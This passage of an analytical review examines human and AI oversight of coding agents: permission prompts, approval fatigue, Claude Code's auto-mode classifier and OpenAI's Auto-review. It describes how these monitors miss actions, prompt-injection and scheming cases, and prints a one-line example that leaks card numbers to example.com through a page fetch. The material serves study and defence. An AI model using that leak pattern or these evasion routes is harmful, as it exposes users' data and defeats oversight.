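| Classifier blocked | 137 | 800 | 937 |
| Classifier allowed | 6 | 110 | 116 |
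| Total | 143 | 910 | 1,053 |

The false negative rates were 86.4% for people and 11.0% for the classifier. People added little as a second check, since they caught only six of the 116 commands the classifier missed.

The testers blocked about 17% of the dangerous commands that came early in a session and about 5% of those that came after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed flat. This fits *approval fatigue*, the tendency to pay less attention to each request as requests pile up. Fatigue may not explain the whole drop. Anthropic doesn't report how the vendor chose when to make the swap, and the testers who reached 50 prompts may have been the ones who clicked fastest from the start.

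If the shop required approval for every refund and email, its reviewer would face 80 prompts, and the last 30 would come at the point in a session when the testers caught about one dangerous command in twenty. Approving the script once would keep the reviewer from reaching that point. But the testers missed five out of six dangerous commands even early in a session, and one wrong approval of the script could allow 80 wrong actions.

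### How far the 13.6% applies elsewhere

The testers had nothing of their own at stake. A developer who could lose a real database might read scripts more carefully than someone working in an unfamiliar environment that a vendor will delete afterwards. Knowing about the evaluation could also have made the testers more alert, or more eager to finish the coding task quickly.

Anthropic also had an interest in the result, since it published the study to justify making auto mode the default. A reviewer who blocked every command would have scored 100%, and the article doesn't give the study's false positive rates, so readers can't tell how often each reviewer blocked safe commands.

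Despite the headline figure, Anthropic still recommends that people personally review high-stakes changes to production systems. When it first described auto mode, it conceded that switching to it is "arguably a regression" for someone who approves every action carefully.

Two independent tests found much higher catch rates. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant through 18 scripted actions representing one day of its work. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had asked for, such as buying a 25-dollar airport lounge pass or reading private messages. The 34 people who had to approve every action blocked 59.6% of this overreach.

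The other test was a browser game in which players approved or denied a coding agent's commands under time pressure. scalex.dev's *Humans missed 1 in 3 threats approving AI agent commands* (2026) analyses about 409,000 of their decisions. The average player caught about two thirds of the threats.

Differences between the tasks probably explain much of the gap. In both tests, about a third of the actions should have been blocked, whereas Anthropic's testers saw one dangerous command in a session of otherwise ordinary prompts. The players also knew they were looking for threats. Yan's participants reviewed only 18 actions, and each prompt described the action in plain language, including any amount or recipient.

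So the 13.6% rate depends on the conditions of the review. It is the most relevant of these figures for daily work, where dangerous requests are rare and come without warning, but the higher rates suggest that people do better when they expect trouble and can see the consequences.

The game also measured how often players blocked safe commands. They blocked the harmless command `rm -rf dist/`, which deletes a project's build files, 45% of the time. About 35% of players caught every threat, but only 21% did so while blocking no more than one in five safe commands.

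Willison (2026), an outside developer, responds to Anthropic's study in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*. He accepts that constant confirmation doesn't produce safe behaviour, but points to the 11% of commands that the classifier missed. He would rather run agents without access to data or tools that could do harm if somebody misdirected the agents.

### Harm in real sessions

Anthropic also examined real use of Claude Code in May and June 2026, where users' own projects were at risk. It took sessions that its safety pipeline had flagged, from accounts that had agreed to the use of their data, and had a model grade each one on two scales from 0 to 10. The first measured the severity of any harm, where 7 meant damage such as deleting rows from a production database. The second measured how explicitly the user had asked for the action.

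Among flagged sessions with manual approval, 6.3% contained harm of severity 7 or more that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4% in auto mode. Manual sessions also had a higher share at every other severity level Anthropic tested.

These figures answer the objection about stakes, but the two groups of sessions may not be comparable, because auto mode was still optional at the time and users chose their own mode. Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* lists manual mode as best for "Sensitive work, unfamiliar code", where the same mistake can do more damage. There could also be a bias in the other direction, since the same guide recommends auto mode for long tasks, which give an agent more time to cause harm.

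The published gap could also appear even if both modes were equally safe, because it compares only flagged sessions. Suppose manual and auto mode each had 10,000 sessions, and 10 in each mode caused serious harm. If the pipeline flagged those 10 and 150 others in manual mode, the share of flagged sessions that caused serious harm would be 10/160, or 6.3%. If it flagged those 10 and 390 others in auto mode, perhaps because more auto sessions contained suspicious but harmless attempts, the share would be 10/400, or 2.5%. There is no evidence that this happened, but nobody outside the company can rule it out without the number of unflagged sessions.

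The production figures are weak evidence that auto mode is safer, but they make it harder to argue that people with something to lose review well enough to make manual approval clearly better. Randomly assigning users to the two modes would be a much better test.

### Approved prompts and rejected plans

Anthropic reports that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts; an earlier figure was 93%. A high approval rate alone doesn't show carelessness, because if one prompt in a thousand were dangerous, a perfect reviewer would approve 99.9%. The AI reviewer OpenAI built for its coding agent, Codex, approves around 99% of the actions it checks, according to *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026).

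The fall in the testers' catch rate and users' own reports are better evidence of fatigue. In *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) asked 107 software practitioners how they handle permission requests. Just under half said they read them carefully, a third skim them, and a fifth approve by default. A third had become less careful over time. One interviewee complained that "every 10 seconds I have to click something".

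Users respond very differently to plans, rejecting 39% of those Claude Code presents for approval. Anthropic takes this as a sign that people scrutinize plans more than prompts.

Users may reject a plan without seeing any danger in it, though. The only negative option in Claude Code's plan prompt is "No, keep planning", after which the user tells the model what to change, so someone who wants a different file format would choose it too. Users can also form an opinion about a plan more easily than about a routine command, which usually has one sensible answer.

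A survey of 203 developers suggests that most objections concern the task. Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026), in *From Delegation to Action Approval*, asked why developers step in while an agent is working:

| Reason for stepping in | Share of developers |
|---|---|
| The agent misunderstood the task or went in the wrong direction | 65% |
| It chose a wrong or overcomplicated approach | 54% |
| It changed more than the developer had requested | 51% |
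| It was about to modify files it shouldn't touch | 35% |
| It was about to run a risky or destructive command | 34% |

The question covered interventions in general rather than rejected plans, but it is likely that people object to plans for similar reasons.

Judging whether a plan is risky can't always be separated from judging whether it is what the user wants. If the user asked only which customers had paid twice, a plan to refund them goes beyond the request. The user might reject it just because they didn't want refunds, and would still prevent 80 unauthorized actions. The problem with the concert tickets is harder to catch. The user has no reason to object to a plan that says "find duplicates", but might object to one that says "treat two charges with the same customer and amount as duplicates".

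The 39% therefore shows that people read plans closely enough to want changes, but not how often they would notice a dangerous step. Nobody appears to have planted a dangerous step to test this.

A script has features of both a plan and a command. Like a plan, it covers a whole task and comes up once, so the user may well engage with it. But it is written in code, like a command, so the prompt may look like one more request to run something. The user's reaction could depend on whether the request leads with the phases or the code. Salerno and colleagues recommend that tools let users distinguish between refusing one action and refusing an approach. For the refund script, the user could then say "don't send the emails" or "this isn't how to find duplicates", and the model could rewrite the relevant part.

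### How users stop the prompts

Many users reduce prompts by writing *allow-rules*, which let matching commands run without approval. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written at least one for shell commands, and the share was growing by about five percentage points every five weeks. Anthropic reports that 5% allow any shell command and another 43% have rules such as `Bash(python:*)`, which allows every command that starts with `python`. It doesn't make clear whether these two shares are of all users or only of those with rules.

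A rule that approves the Python interpreter allows any Python script. This is nearly as broad as approving everything, because a Python script can delete files or start other programs. If the shop's agent ran the refund script as `python refund.py`, the rule would allow both that script and a version that refunded every charge.

Trębacz and colleagues at OpenAI found the same habit inside the company, where a "sizable minority" of users allow all commands that begin with `python`. One user's settings let the agent launch another copy of itself with its protections switched off.

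Others turn off the prompts altogether. In Claude Code, 62% of users have used the mode that bypasses permissions or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions start in bypass mode. If prompts are too frequent, users may therefore review very little. Auto mode ignores allow rules broad enough to run arbitrary code, so its classifier still checks those commands, but the rules apply again when the user leaves auto mode.

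Even without such a rule, a prompt may name a script without showing it. In the browser game, players most often missed the threat in `npm run analyze`, which runs whatever command the project has stored under "analyze". The stored command sent data to an outside server. Players could see it in the agent's history just above the prompt, but 64.7% approved the run. Across three threats of this kind, players missed 52.5%, compared with 28.4% of other attempts to steal data or run hostile code. A workflow prompt that shows only a name and some phases might have the same weakness.

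Carefully reviewing code doesn't seem to stop developers from approving agents' actions without close review. In the survey by Wu and colleagues, 61% of developers who carefully reviewed most or all generated code often approved at least one type of action without close review, compared with 67% of the others, a difference that could be due to chance. Developers who knew of security incidents involving agents were more likely to approve actions this way than those who didn't (70% against 43%). The link remained after the researchers accounted for how much the developers used agents. The developers reported their own behavior, so the figures show habits rather than the number of dangerous actions approved.

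Yan tested whether people could reduce prompts by setting rules in advance. Before the simulated day began, 35 participants chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four consequences: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something, and reading private data. They chose "ask" for 114 of the 140 rules, which postponed most decisions until the agent was about to act.

These participants saw an average of 10.9 prompts, compared with 18 in the group that had to review every action. But when a prompt concerned overreach, they approved it 66.8% of the time, compared with 40.3% in the other group. Counting the actions that their rules blocked or allowed automatically, they stopped only about 40% of the overreach. The approval rates aren't directly comparable, because each person's rules determined which prompts appeared. They still give a reason to doubt that people will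 review more strictly just because a script replaces 80 prompts with one.

### Reading generated code

No one appears to have measured how well people judge tool-orchestration scripts before they run. The closest evidence comes from people who reviewed finished code or finished work by agents.

In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) gave 36 people short programming tasks and an agent that wrote the Python. In some tasks, the agent's code contained a defect that the provided checks didn't reveal. The researchers warned participants in the instructions that these checks covered only basic functions. Participants could read and edit the code, run it on their own examples, and question the agent.

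Participants fixed 28 of 71 hidden defects, or 39%. Their confidence did not reliably indicate success. In 34 of the 43 failed cases, they rated their confidence that the solution was correct at 4 or 5 out of 5. The share of defects fixed rose with experience, from 17% for beginners to 39% for intermediate programmers and 57% for advanced ones, although the beginner and advanced groups had only six and seven people, respectively.

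One task resembles the refund script. The code had to total a member's charges, but the defective version ignored refunds instead of subtracting them. Participants fixed this defect 75% of the time, compared with 8% for the hardest defect. Rerunning the supplied example might not expose it, but entering a charge and an equal refund would, because the total should then be zero.

Lack of effort doesn't explain most of the failures, since participants did more than the required check in 65 of the 71 cases. But in only 40 did they examine a risk specific to the task. In 35 cases they produced evidence that could have revealed the defect, and in five of those they misread it. Participants who were shown their results after the first round fixed 51% of defects in the second, up from 28%. They recognised more of the defects, though they didn't check more often.

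A reviewer at the shop would have some advantages, because the refund script has only seven lines and the reviewer knows the business. But the reviewer can't test the script by running it as is, because that would send the refunds. A test would need made-up charges and harmless replacements for `issue_refund` and `send_email`, and someone would still have to think to include two concert tickets among the charges.

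### Whether summaries help

A summary could help by pointing the reviewer to the right question. At Microsoft Research, Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues (2026), in *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight*, compared three ways of summarizing what a web-browsing agent had done. Twelve participants had to decide whether the agent's answer to a question was correct:

| Type of summary | Correct judgements when the answer was wrong | Correct judgements overall | Average time |
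|---|---|---|---|
| Flowchart of the agent's steps | 39% | 57% | 391 seconds |
| Text with links to the evidence | 52% | 63% | 390 seconds |
| List of requirements and assumptions | 65% | 77% | 525 seconds |

Participants who accepted a wrong answer often said that the agent's process looked reasonable. The flowchart encouraged this because it showed sensible steps but not whether the agent had carried them out properly. A list of phases in an approval prompt has a similar weakness, because "Find duplicates" is a reasonable step even if line 3 does it badly.

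The differences are only suggestive, because the sample was small and each type of summary came with its own questions. The researchers also wrote the summaries by hand, and a summary written by a model might omit the assumption that matters.

They then built an interface around requirements and assumptions and tested it in another small study of 12 people. Participants found errors faster than with the agent's ordinary record of its work, but their accuracy didn't improve meaningfully. When they missed an error, they were more confident that the agent was right. A clearer summary can therefore make reviewers more confident in a wrong approval.

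For the refund script, such a summary would at least state what the phrase "charged twice" conceals:

- Two charges count as duplicates if the customer and amount match, even if the purchases were weeks apart.
- All guests without an account count as the same customer.
- Each email goes out immediately after its refund, with no limit on the number of either.

A reviewer who doesn't read Python could object to any of these lines. However, the list is useful as a gate only if it matches the code. If the same model writes both, it may leave out an assumption it made implicitly, and the reviewer would have to go back to line 3 to find it.

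## AI models as reviewers

An AI reviewer reads Python as easily as prose, and in Anthropic's study its 89% catch rate didn't fall as sessions went on. But before the refund script runs, it has no more information about the November charges than a person does, unless somebody supplies the facts.

Anthropic and OpenAI have each published the design and error rates of an AI reviewer. Anthropic's is the classifier behind Claude Code's auto mode, which has since become the default for interactive sessions in the terminal and VS Code. OpenAI's is Auto-review, part of Codex. Both companies built their reviewers for coding agents and report results mainly for single actions.

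### How auto mode reaches a decision

Many actions never reach the classifier. Anthropic documents a fixed order, in which the first step that applies decides:

1. If the user has written a rule for the action, Claude Code follows it and allows the action, refuses it or asks.
2. If the action only reads data, or edits a file in the working directory, Claude Code allows it. Users can inspect such edits later through version control.
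3. Everything else goes to the classifier, including shell commands, web requests and calls to external tools.

Changes to protected files, such as Claude Code's own configuration, go to the classifier even if a rule allows them. Narrow allow-rules otherwise still apply, and Anthropic warns that they can let a destructive argument through without review. An optional setting sends nearly all shell commands to the classifier instead.

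The refund script would reach step 3 because it calls external tools that change something. The classifier then works in up to two stages. In the fast first stage, it outputs a single token, yes or no, under an instruction to err on the side of blocking. The action runs unless the classifier flags it, in which case the same model gets the same text with a new final instruction and reasons step by step before it decides. Because only the final instruction differs, the system can reuse nearly all of its processing from the first stage.

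The text contains a fixed template on how to interpret actions and consent, followed by the organisation's policy. The policy names the trusted infrastructure and sorts rules into four levels:

- **Hard denies** block an action whatever the user has said. The built-in one covers sending data such as code or secrets to outsiders.
- **Soft denies** block destructive actions, such as overwriting a repository's history, unless one of the next two levels applies.
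- **Exceptions** clear routine cases that a soft deny would catch.
- **Explicit intent** clears the remaining soft denies, but only if the user's message describes the exact action.

When Claude Code blocks an action, the session continues. The agent receives the denial as the result of its tool call, with an instruction to find a safer way and not to work around the block. In most sessions, the only reason now given is "Blocked by classifier". After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. In March 2026, a session with no user to ask ended at that point. According to the September documentation, such a session continues without running the blocked action.

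Wrongly blocking a single command does little harm, since the agent usually finds another way. If the classifier wrongly blocked the refund script, the agent would have to rewrite the program, perhaps without the emails, and the classifier would have to review the new version.

### Scripts that assemble a command

The template tells the classifier to judge what an action does rather than how it looks. If the agent joins several commands into a chain, the whole chain counts as one action. If it writes a program to a file and runs the file later, the classifier judges the program. If a Python script puts together a shell command, the classifier has to work out the finished command from the conversation before the script may run. Take these two lines:

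```python
folder = "build"
subprocess.run(["rm", "-rf", folder])
```

The classifier can substitute the value of `folder` and judge `rm -rf build`, which deletes a folder of build files. It couldn't do this if the value came from an earlier command's output, because it never receives that output.

Anthropic added a rule to auto mode that blocks a recursive forced delete if its target is a shell variable that nothing in the visible conversation sets. The block clears once the user names the exact path or the agent repeats the command with the path written out.

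Line 5 of the refund script has the same gap, because the charge numbers and amounts come from data that the classifier hasn't seen. A similar rule for refunds would block the script, and so would a strict trust check. To clear the block, the agent could print the 40 duplicates, read them, and write a second script that lists each charge number and amount, so that the reviewer would see the actual values.

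### Why the reviewer works without explanations or results

The classifier reads the user's messages, the project's standing instructions and the agent's tool calls, except read-only lookups. Claude Code removes everything the agent wrote in its own words and the results of tool calls.

Anthropic removes the agent's explanations so that the agent can't persuade the reviewer to approve its actions. An agent might write that the user had implicitly approved a deletion, or that a target definitely belonged to the agent, and the reviewer might believe it. In the shop, the agent might describe the 40 charges as "confirmed duplicates", although its only evidence is that the customers and amounts match.

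Removing tool results from the classifier's input protects against prompt injection. Suppose a file contains an instruction to send the project's passwords to a web address, and the agent obeys. The classifier compares the attempt to send passwords to an outside address with what the user asked for. It never reads the file, so the planted text cannot persuade it.

Anthropic also found that adding the agent's messages and the tool results to the classifier's input made it worse at catching overeager actions, perhaps because the longer record is harder to read and contains more of the agent's framing. Given only the tool calls, the classifier had the lowest miss rate but blocked things users had plainly requested.

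*AgentBouncer* (2026) mediates a coding agent's access to the system. Its reviewer reads the agent's explanation of each tool call as well as the call itself. The explanation can show why an unusual step is necessary, but it also gives the agent a way to influence the decision.

A drawback of auto mode's design is that the classifier can't tell where a value came from. If the agent cancels "job abc123" and the user never mentioned that job, the agent may have found the ID in a query or invented it. Anthropic accepts this in return for protection against planted instructions. The shop would have the same problem with a second script that had 40 charge numbers written out, because the classifier couldn't check that any of them belonged to a duplicate.

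A separate scanner partly makes up for what the classifier doesn't read. It searches tool results for planted instructions before the results enter the agent's context, and adds a warning if it finds any. When the agent runs a script, this scanner would have little to examine beyond the printed output.

### Error rates and misread consent

Anthropic published results for each stage in March 2026:

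| | Harmless actions blocked, in 10,000 real tool calls | Harmful actions missed, of 52 real overeager ones | Harmful actions missed, of 1,000 synthetic leaks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The reasoning stage examines only the actions that the fast stage has flagged, so it can release actions but cannot block any that the fast stage let through. It released about 95% of the harmless actions it examined, but also about 11% of the overeager actions and 4% of the leaks.

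Anthropic calls the 17% "the honest number" because those 52 actions came from real sessions. But the sample is small, and nine actions out of 52 is compatible with a true rate anywhere from about 9% to 30%. The sample also includes only actions that an employee refused or somebody flagged afterwards, so it may lack actions that nobody noticed. Anthropic generated the leaks, so they were easier to produce in large numbers.

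In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but misjudged whether the user had consented. In one case, a user had written "Clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed set of changes), and the agent tried to overwrite the history on the server. In another, the classifier treated the user's earlier approval of a similar action as approval of the new one. Anthropic tried to fix the problem by rewording the instructions, but the drawbacks of every attempt outweighed the benefits.

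The rule on explicit intent addresses the same weakness. Under it, a request to "force-push this branch" authorises overwriting history, but a request to "clean up the repo" doesn't. Hard denies apply regardless of consent, so the classifier can't get the decision wrong by misreading consent. But a shop that wants an agent to issue refunds could hardly put them under a hard deny.

It would also be hard to tell whether the user consented to everything in the refund script. If the user asked the agent to "sort out the double charges", the classifier should block the script, because the user didn't ask for refunds. If the user wrote "refund everyone who was charged twice in November", that would be clear consent to the refunds but not to the emails. Even if the request covered both, it would be unclear whether the user consented to refunding the concert tickets, since they agreed only to refund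 double charges.

In another of Anthropic's examples, a user said "cancel my job", and the agent searched a computing cluster, picked the job with the most similar name and tried to delete it. Auto mode blocks this because the agent inferred the target, and the job might have belonged to someone else. The refund script infers 40 targets in the same way. Under a strict reading, the policy would block the script until the user confirmed which charges to refund, even if they had clearly asked for refunds.

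### Facts about the current state

The command `git reset --hard` returns a project's files to their last saved version. This may destroy a day's work if the files have changed since then and is harmless otherwise, but the command's text is the same in both cases.

By August 2026, Claude Code had begun to run `git status` before commands that could discard work and to give the classifier the missing information about whether there were unsaved changes or new files. The agent isn't involved in this check, so it can't misreport the result.

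A second fact is where code is going, since uploading it to the team's private repository is routine but uploading it to a public one may be a leak. In August, Anthropic described a check on whether the destination is public, private or trusted. However, the October documentation shows that the classifier assumes a repository is private unless its address or something in the readable conversation indicates otherwise. User messages reach the classifier but tool results don't, so it doesn't receive the answer if the agent looks up the repository's visibility. A wrong assumption mainly endangers confidential material, because the rules on secrets and personal data apply to private repositories too.

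Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, tested the classifier by inserting synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions, and shared successful ones with Anthropic. Anthropic strengthened the classifier, mainly by giving it repository visibility, the state of the files and clearer rules on handling data. Apollo then tested it again with attacks it had withheld. The classifier caught about half of those it had previously missed, and missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. Across the shared and withheld attacks, the share it missed fell from 12% to 7%.

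The withheld attacks are the better evidence, because Anthropic couldn't have tuned the classifier to them. But the test doesn't separate the effect of the new facts from that of the new rules. Anthropic also points out that the attacks were more malicious than anything Claude does unprompted, so 7% isn't an estimate for ordinary use.

The March error rates are also dated, because the classifier ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6 then, and by September it ran on Sonnet 5 by default.

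For the shop, useful facts would include the number of refunds, their total, the largest single amount and the number of guests without an account. Claude Code lets a developer's own software attach a note to a tool result, and the classifier reads the note but not the result. The shop could use the note to report that November has 40 apparent duplicates. Counts and sums leave an attacker almost no room for instructions, but quoting charge descriptions in the note would let planted text back in.

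The facts must also come from a source other than the script. If the shop's software counted duplicates by customer and amount, as the script does, it would report the same 40, which would look like confirmation. A count of matching charges made more than an hour apart would give the reviewer new information.

An organisation can replace the human reviewer with an AI model. Wu and colleagues' system reports a shell command's observed effects and can undo them. They also connected their AI reviewer to Claude Code as the only check on its actions.

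### A test with planted instructions

Anthropic commissioned another evaluation from the company Trajectory Labs. The evaluation used 72 scenarios in which planted text is meant to make an agent leak data, commit fraud or help steal a user's login details. Trajectory Labs ran each scenario ten times, for a total of 720 attempts per model. Anthropic didn't have access to the scenarios.

| Agent | Attacks that succeeded without a reviewer | Attacks that succeeded with a reviewer |
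|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 | 0.09% on average across Anthropic's latest models | 0% |
| Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol | 19.03% | 5.83% |

These figures provide little evidence about auto mode, because the Claude models resisted nearly every attack without it. They provide more evidence about Auto-review, which reduced successful attacks in Codex from 137 to 42, though the runs without a reviewer also had wider access, so the sandbox may account for some of the drop.

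The 720 attempts are weaker evidence than 720 independent tests would be, because they consist of ten runs of each of 72 scenarios. If runs of the same scenario tend to end alike, zero successes in 72 scenarios still allow a true success rate of about 4%.

Anthropic paid for the comparison and published it while making auto mode the default. The attackers had optimised their texts against Claude Opus 4.7, which gave none of the tested models an obvious advantage. Trajectory Labs used its own browser connection, which left out the safeguards in both companies' browser extensions. OpenAI had released a newer version of Auto-review by the time Anthropic published the results.

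### OpenAI's Auto-review

Codex confines the agent to a sandbox. By default, the agent can read files, edit those in its working folder and run local commands, but can't use the network. Actions within these limits get no review. To go beyond them, the agent has to ask permission, and a second Codex agent answers in place of the user.

OpenAI's *Auto-review* documents what that second agent receives, which differs considerably from auto mode:

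| | Auto mode | Auto-review |
|---|---|---|
| User's messages | yes | yes |
| Agent's tool calls | yes, except read-only lookups | the relevant ones |
| Agent's explanations | no | visible updates, but not hidden reasoning |
| Tool results | no | the relevant ones |
| Current state | supplied before certain commands | the reviewer can run read-only checks, but rarely does |
| Repeated denials | after 3 in a row or 20 in a session, the user decides | after 3 in a row or 10 of the last 50, the turn ends |

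If the agent had already listed the charges with a direct call, Auto-review could see them and might recognise the concert tickets. But it would also read whatever customers had written in those records. *ClawSentry* (2026), which describes another monitor for agents, argues for restricting such a reviewer to read-only tools so that it can't run commands or change files itself if planted text misleads it. A misled reviewer could still approve a harmful request from the agent.

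The sandbox boundary doesn't fully cover the shop's refund script, because the script acts through tools that the developer connected. OpenAI also triggers review for tool calls that need approval under their labels or the user's settings. A refund tool without the right label or setting could therefore run without review.

Trębacz and colleagues measured Auto-review's *recall*, the share of harmful actions that it denied. Recall was 90.3% on synthetic cases of overeager behaviour, such as unintended data transfers and irreversible operations, and 99.3% on prompt injections that tried to run remote code, steal secrets or upload data. Recall on prompt injections falls to 90.2% when deletions and tampering are included, but many of the additional misses were actions that Auto-review rated too minor to block, and the researchers often agreed.

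Auto-review had a recall of 90.3%, so it missed 9.7% of overeager actions, while auto mode missed 17%. The difference doesn't show that Auto-review is the better reviewer, because OpenAI tested it on synthetic cases and Anthropic took its 52 cases from real sessions.

Trębacz and colleagues warn against treating Auto-review as a security guarantee, and in their own tests it could sometimes be misled into approving commands. They also don't present it as protection against *scheming*, in which a model strategically hides its aims. Such a model could word its request to look harmless, or do damage inside the sandbox, where Auto-review doesn't check its actions. They recommend other kinds of monitoring for scheming, including monitoring the model's reasoning.

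This is compatible with Anthropic's view of its own classifier. Because the classifier ignores the agent's reasoning, it can still stop a model that conceals its aims, as long as the action itself breaks a rule. A harmful refund that looks like the other 39 wouldn't break a rule, so the classifier wouldn't stop it.

### From single actions to whole scripts

Auto mode treats a script as one action, and some of the 10,000 tool calls in Anthropic's sample probably ran scripts, but none of these error rates is reported separately for scripts.

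The per-call rates also can't be converted to per-script rates by simple arithmetic, because errors on 80 similar calls are unlikely to be independent. For the refund script, a reviewer with a false positive rate of 0.4% per call could interrupt anywhere from under 1% to 27% of harmless runs, and only a test on scripts would show the real figure.

In one of OpenAI's measurements, Auto-review scored 96.1% on a benchmark of whole action sequences, where a sequence counted as caught if the reviewer rejected any action in it. That standard is reasonable if the early steps are preparation. But every step of the loop in the refund script is final, so a reviewer could get full credit for an objection that came too late for most customers.

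A reviewer that judges calls one at a time can also miss what they do together. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (2026) tested nine models on leaks that are visible only by comparing two executions. The script that emails "yes" if a card number starts with 4 leaks this way, because it sends an email for some customers and not for others. Each model judged ten such scenarios three times, one action at a time. Eight blocked nothing, and the ninth objected in three of its 30 trials. All nine caught an openly visible leak every time. When the models saw both executions side by side, eight caught the leak in all 30 trials and the other caught it in 17.

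A reviewer that reads the script before it runs has an advantage here, because the text contains the condition and therefore both outcomes, though the reviewer may still overlook the leak. Auto mode treats a limit that the user states in the conversation, such as 100 dollars per refund, as a reason to block matching actions, but only a reviewer that checks each call would see the actual amounts. *AgentBouncer* decides on each concrete request for access while the program runs.

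Auto mode already combines both positions for subagents. The classifier checks the task before a subagent starts, then each of its actions, and finally the whole record of its work. The first check is necessary because the subagent receives the main agent's instruction in place of a user message, so anything the main agent invented would look like a user request. The last check only adds a warning to the result, since the actions have already happened.

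A runtime could treat scripts the same way. Before the run, the reviewer would compare the code with the user's request and look for conditions that leak data. At each call, it would check the actual amount and recipient and keep a running total. The reviewer would still need evidence that the charges were duplicates, because neither the code nor the arguments of a single refund contain it.

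## Approving effects once the data is known

Any reviewer, human or AI, could judge the refund script better after seeing the November charges. A runtime can postpone the decision until then. It can list the script's intended writes before any of them happens, pause at each write until somebody approves it, or check the actual arguments of every call against a written rule.

### Previewing the writes

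To produce a preview, the runtime lets the script read data but replaces the tools that have effects with functions that only take notes:

```python
planned = []

async def issue_refund(charge, amount):
    planned.append(("refund", charge, amount))

async def send_email(to, text):
    planned.append(("email", to, text))
```

The runtime does not change `list_charges` and runs the script's seven lines as written. Afterwards, `planned` contains 80 entries. Software can summarise these for the reviewer, for example as 40 refunds totalling 1,130 dollars, none above 38 dollars, and 40 emails with their addresses. The runtime also has to withhold line 7's output from the model, because the script prints "40 duplicates refunded" before anyone has refunded anything.

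A month with three refunds and a month with three thousand now produce different lists, so a reviewer can approve one and reject the other, which nobody could do reliably from the identical text. The list is also complete in a useful sense. Let *P* be the effects in the preview and *A* the effects of the later run. If the charges haven't changed, then

*A* ⊆ *P*

because the run either makes every call on the list or stops early when a call fails. This holds only because the script ignores what `issue_refund` and `send_email` return. Suppose another script offers store credit whenever a refund fails. The note-taking function has to invent a result for each refund, and if it always reports success, the preview will contain no store credit. The preview also lists only the calls, not what the payment company's servers do when a refund arrives.

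A reviewer can still easily miss the concert tickets. An entry such as "ch_0412, 20 dollars, anna@example.com" looks the same whether Anna was charged twice for one ticket or bought two tickets. The preview would also have to show what she bought, which may take another lookup in the shop's order system. Reviewers can still miss problems when the description is clear, since Yan's participants had a clear description of every action and still approved much of the overreach.

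### Plan, then apply

Terraform, HashiCorp's software for managing servers, already works this way. It sets up servers and databases from text files that describe the desired result. According to HashiCorp's *terraform plan command*, the software reads the current state of the systems, compares it with the description, and proposes a set of changes. It makes no changes until the user applies the plan. Other software can check an exit code to see whether the plan contains any changes, and a shop could use a similar signal to skip the approval in months without duplicates.

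Terraform can compute the changes from the description. A script contains only the steps, so the runtime has to run it to determine what it would do.

After the approval, the shop can either run the script again or carry out the saved list. A second run reads the charges again. If a late charge has arrived, the script may find a 41st duplicate that nobody approved, so the runtime has to compare every call with the approved list. Carrying out the saved list avoids this, but the list may be out of date, because a colleague may have refunded one of the 40 charges by hand since the preview.

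HashiCorp warns that other changes can make the final effect differ from an earlier plan, and advises users to check the final plan again. Its hosted service goes further. If anything else modifies the state before the user confirms a saved plan, the service discards the plan automatically, as HashiCorp documents. *AstronOS* (2026), a runtime for long-running agents, builds the same condition into the commit, the step that makes changes final:

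commit succeeds only if version checked = current version

The runtime has to compare the versions as part of the commit. If it compared them first and committed afterward, the data could change in between.

If any new charge invalidated the preview, a busy shop might never get one approved in time. The shop would need to check only that the 40 charges and their earlier counterparts haven't changed. Even then, it can't combine the check and the refund into a single step unless the payment company offers a refund that goes through only if the charge is still in the expected state.

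*Mind the Gap* (2025) examines this problem in agents, where the time between checking and acting may include the time the model spends thinking. One remedy is a monitor that recognizes pairs of tools vulnerable to a change between the two calls and halts the second call with a warning. Another is to combine the two tools into one operation. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026), a review, reports that these measures, together with rewritten prompts, reduced the share of runs with such a flaw from 12% to 8% on a benchmark of 66 tasks.

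### Reads that disclose data

A preview runs the reads for real, on the assumption that reading is harmless. But a read sends its arguments to whoever answers it. Suppose the script contained this line:

```python
await fetch_page(url=f"https://example.com/?q={c['card']}")
```

A tool that fetches web pages would normally count as a read, so the card numbers would reach whoever runs example.com before the reviewer saw the preview, and the list of planned writes wouldn't mention them. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026), a review of 89 sources, treats even low-risk reads as actions that need authorisation. For a preview, the shop could allow reads only from services that already hold the data, or apply a data-flow check to the arguments of every read.

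The preview can also expose sensitive data. HashiCorp warns that a saved plan file contains sensitive values in readable form even if the terminal display hides them. The shop's preview would contain 40 customers' addresses. An AI reviewer that reads it would also read any text customers wrote in their orders, including any instructions somebody planted there.

### Agent systems that hold effects back

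Some online services offer a "dry run", which tests a request without carrying it out. *GoEX* (Patil, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) proposed that services extend this feature so that users can see and approve the result of an agent's actions before it becomes final. If the payment company offered such a preview, it could include effects on the company's own servers.

Chen, Dong and colleagues (2026), in *Cordon*, built an agent system that comes close to a preview without help from the services. Cordon treats a whole task as one transaction:

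1. Reads run normally, and the system records which results later steps use.
2. Changes to local files go into a shadow copy. The agent sees its own changes when it reads the files again, but nobody else does.
3. Messages and other external effects wait in an outbox.
4. At the end, Cordon checks everything together. It then makes the changes final and releases the outbox, or discards both.

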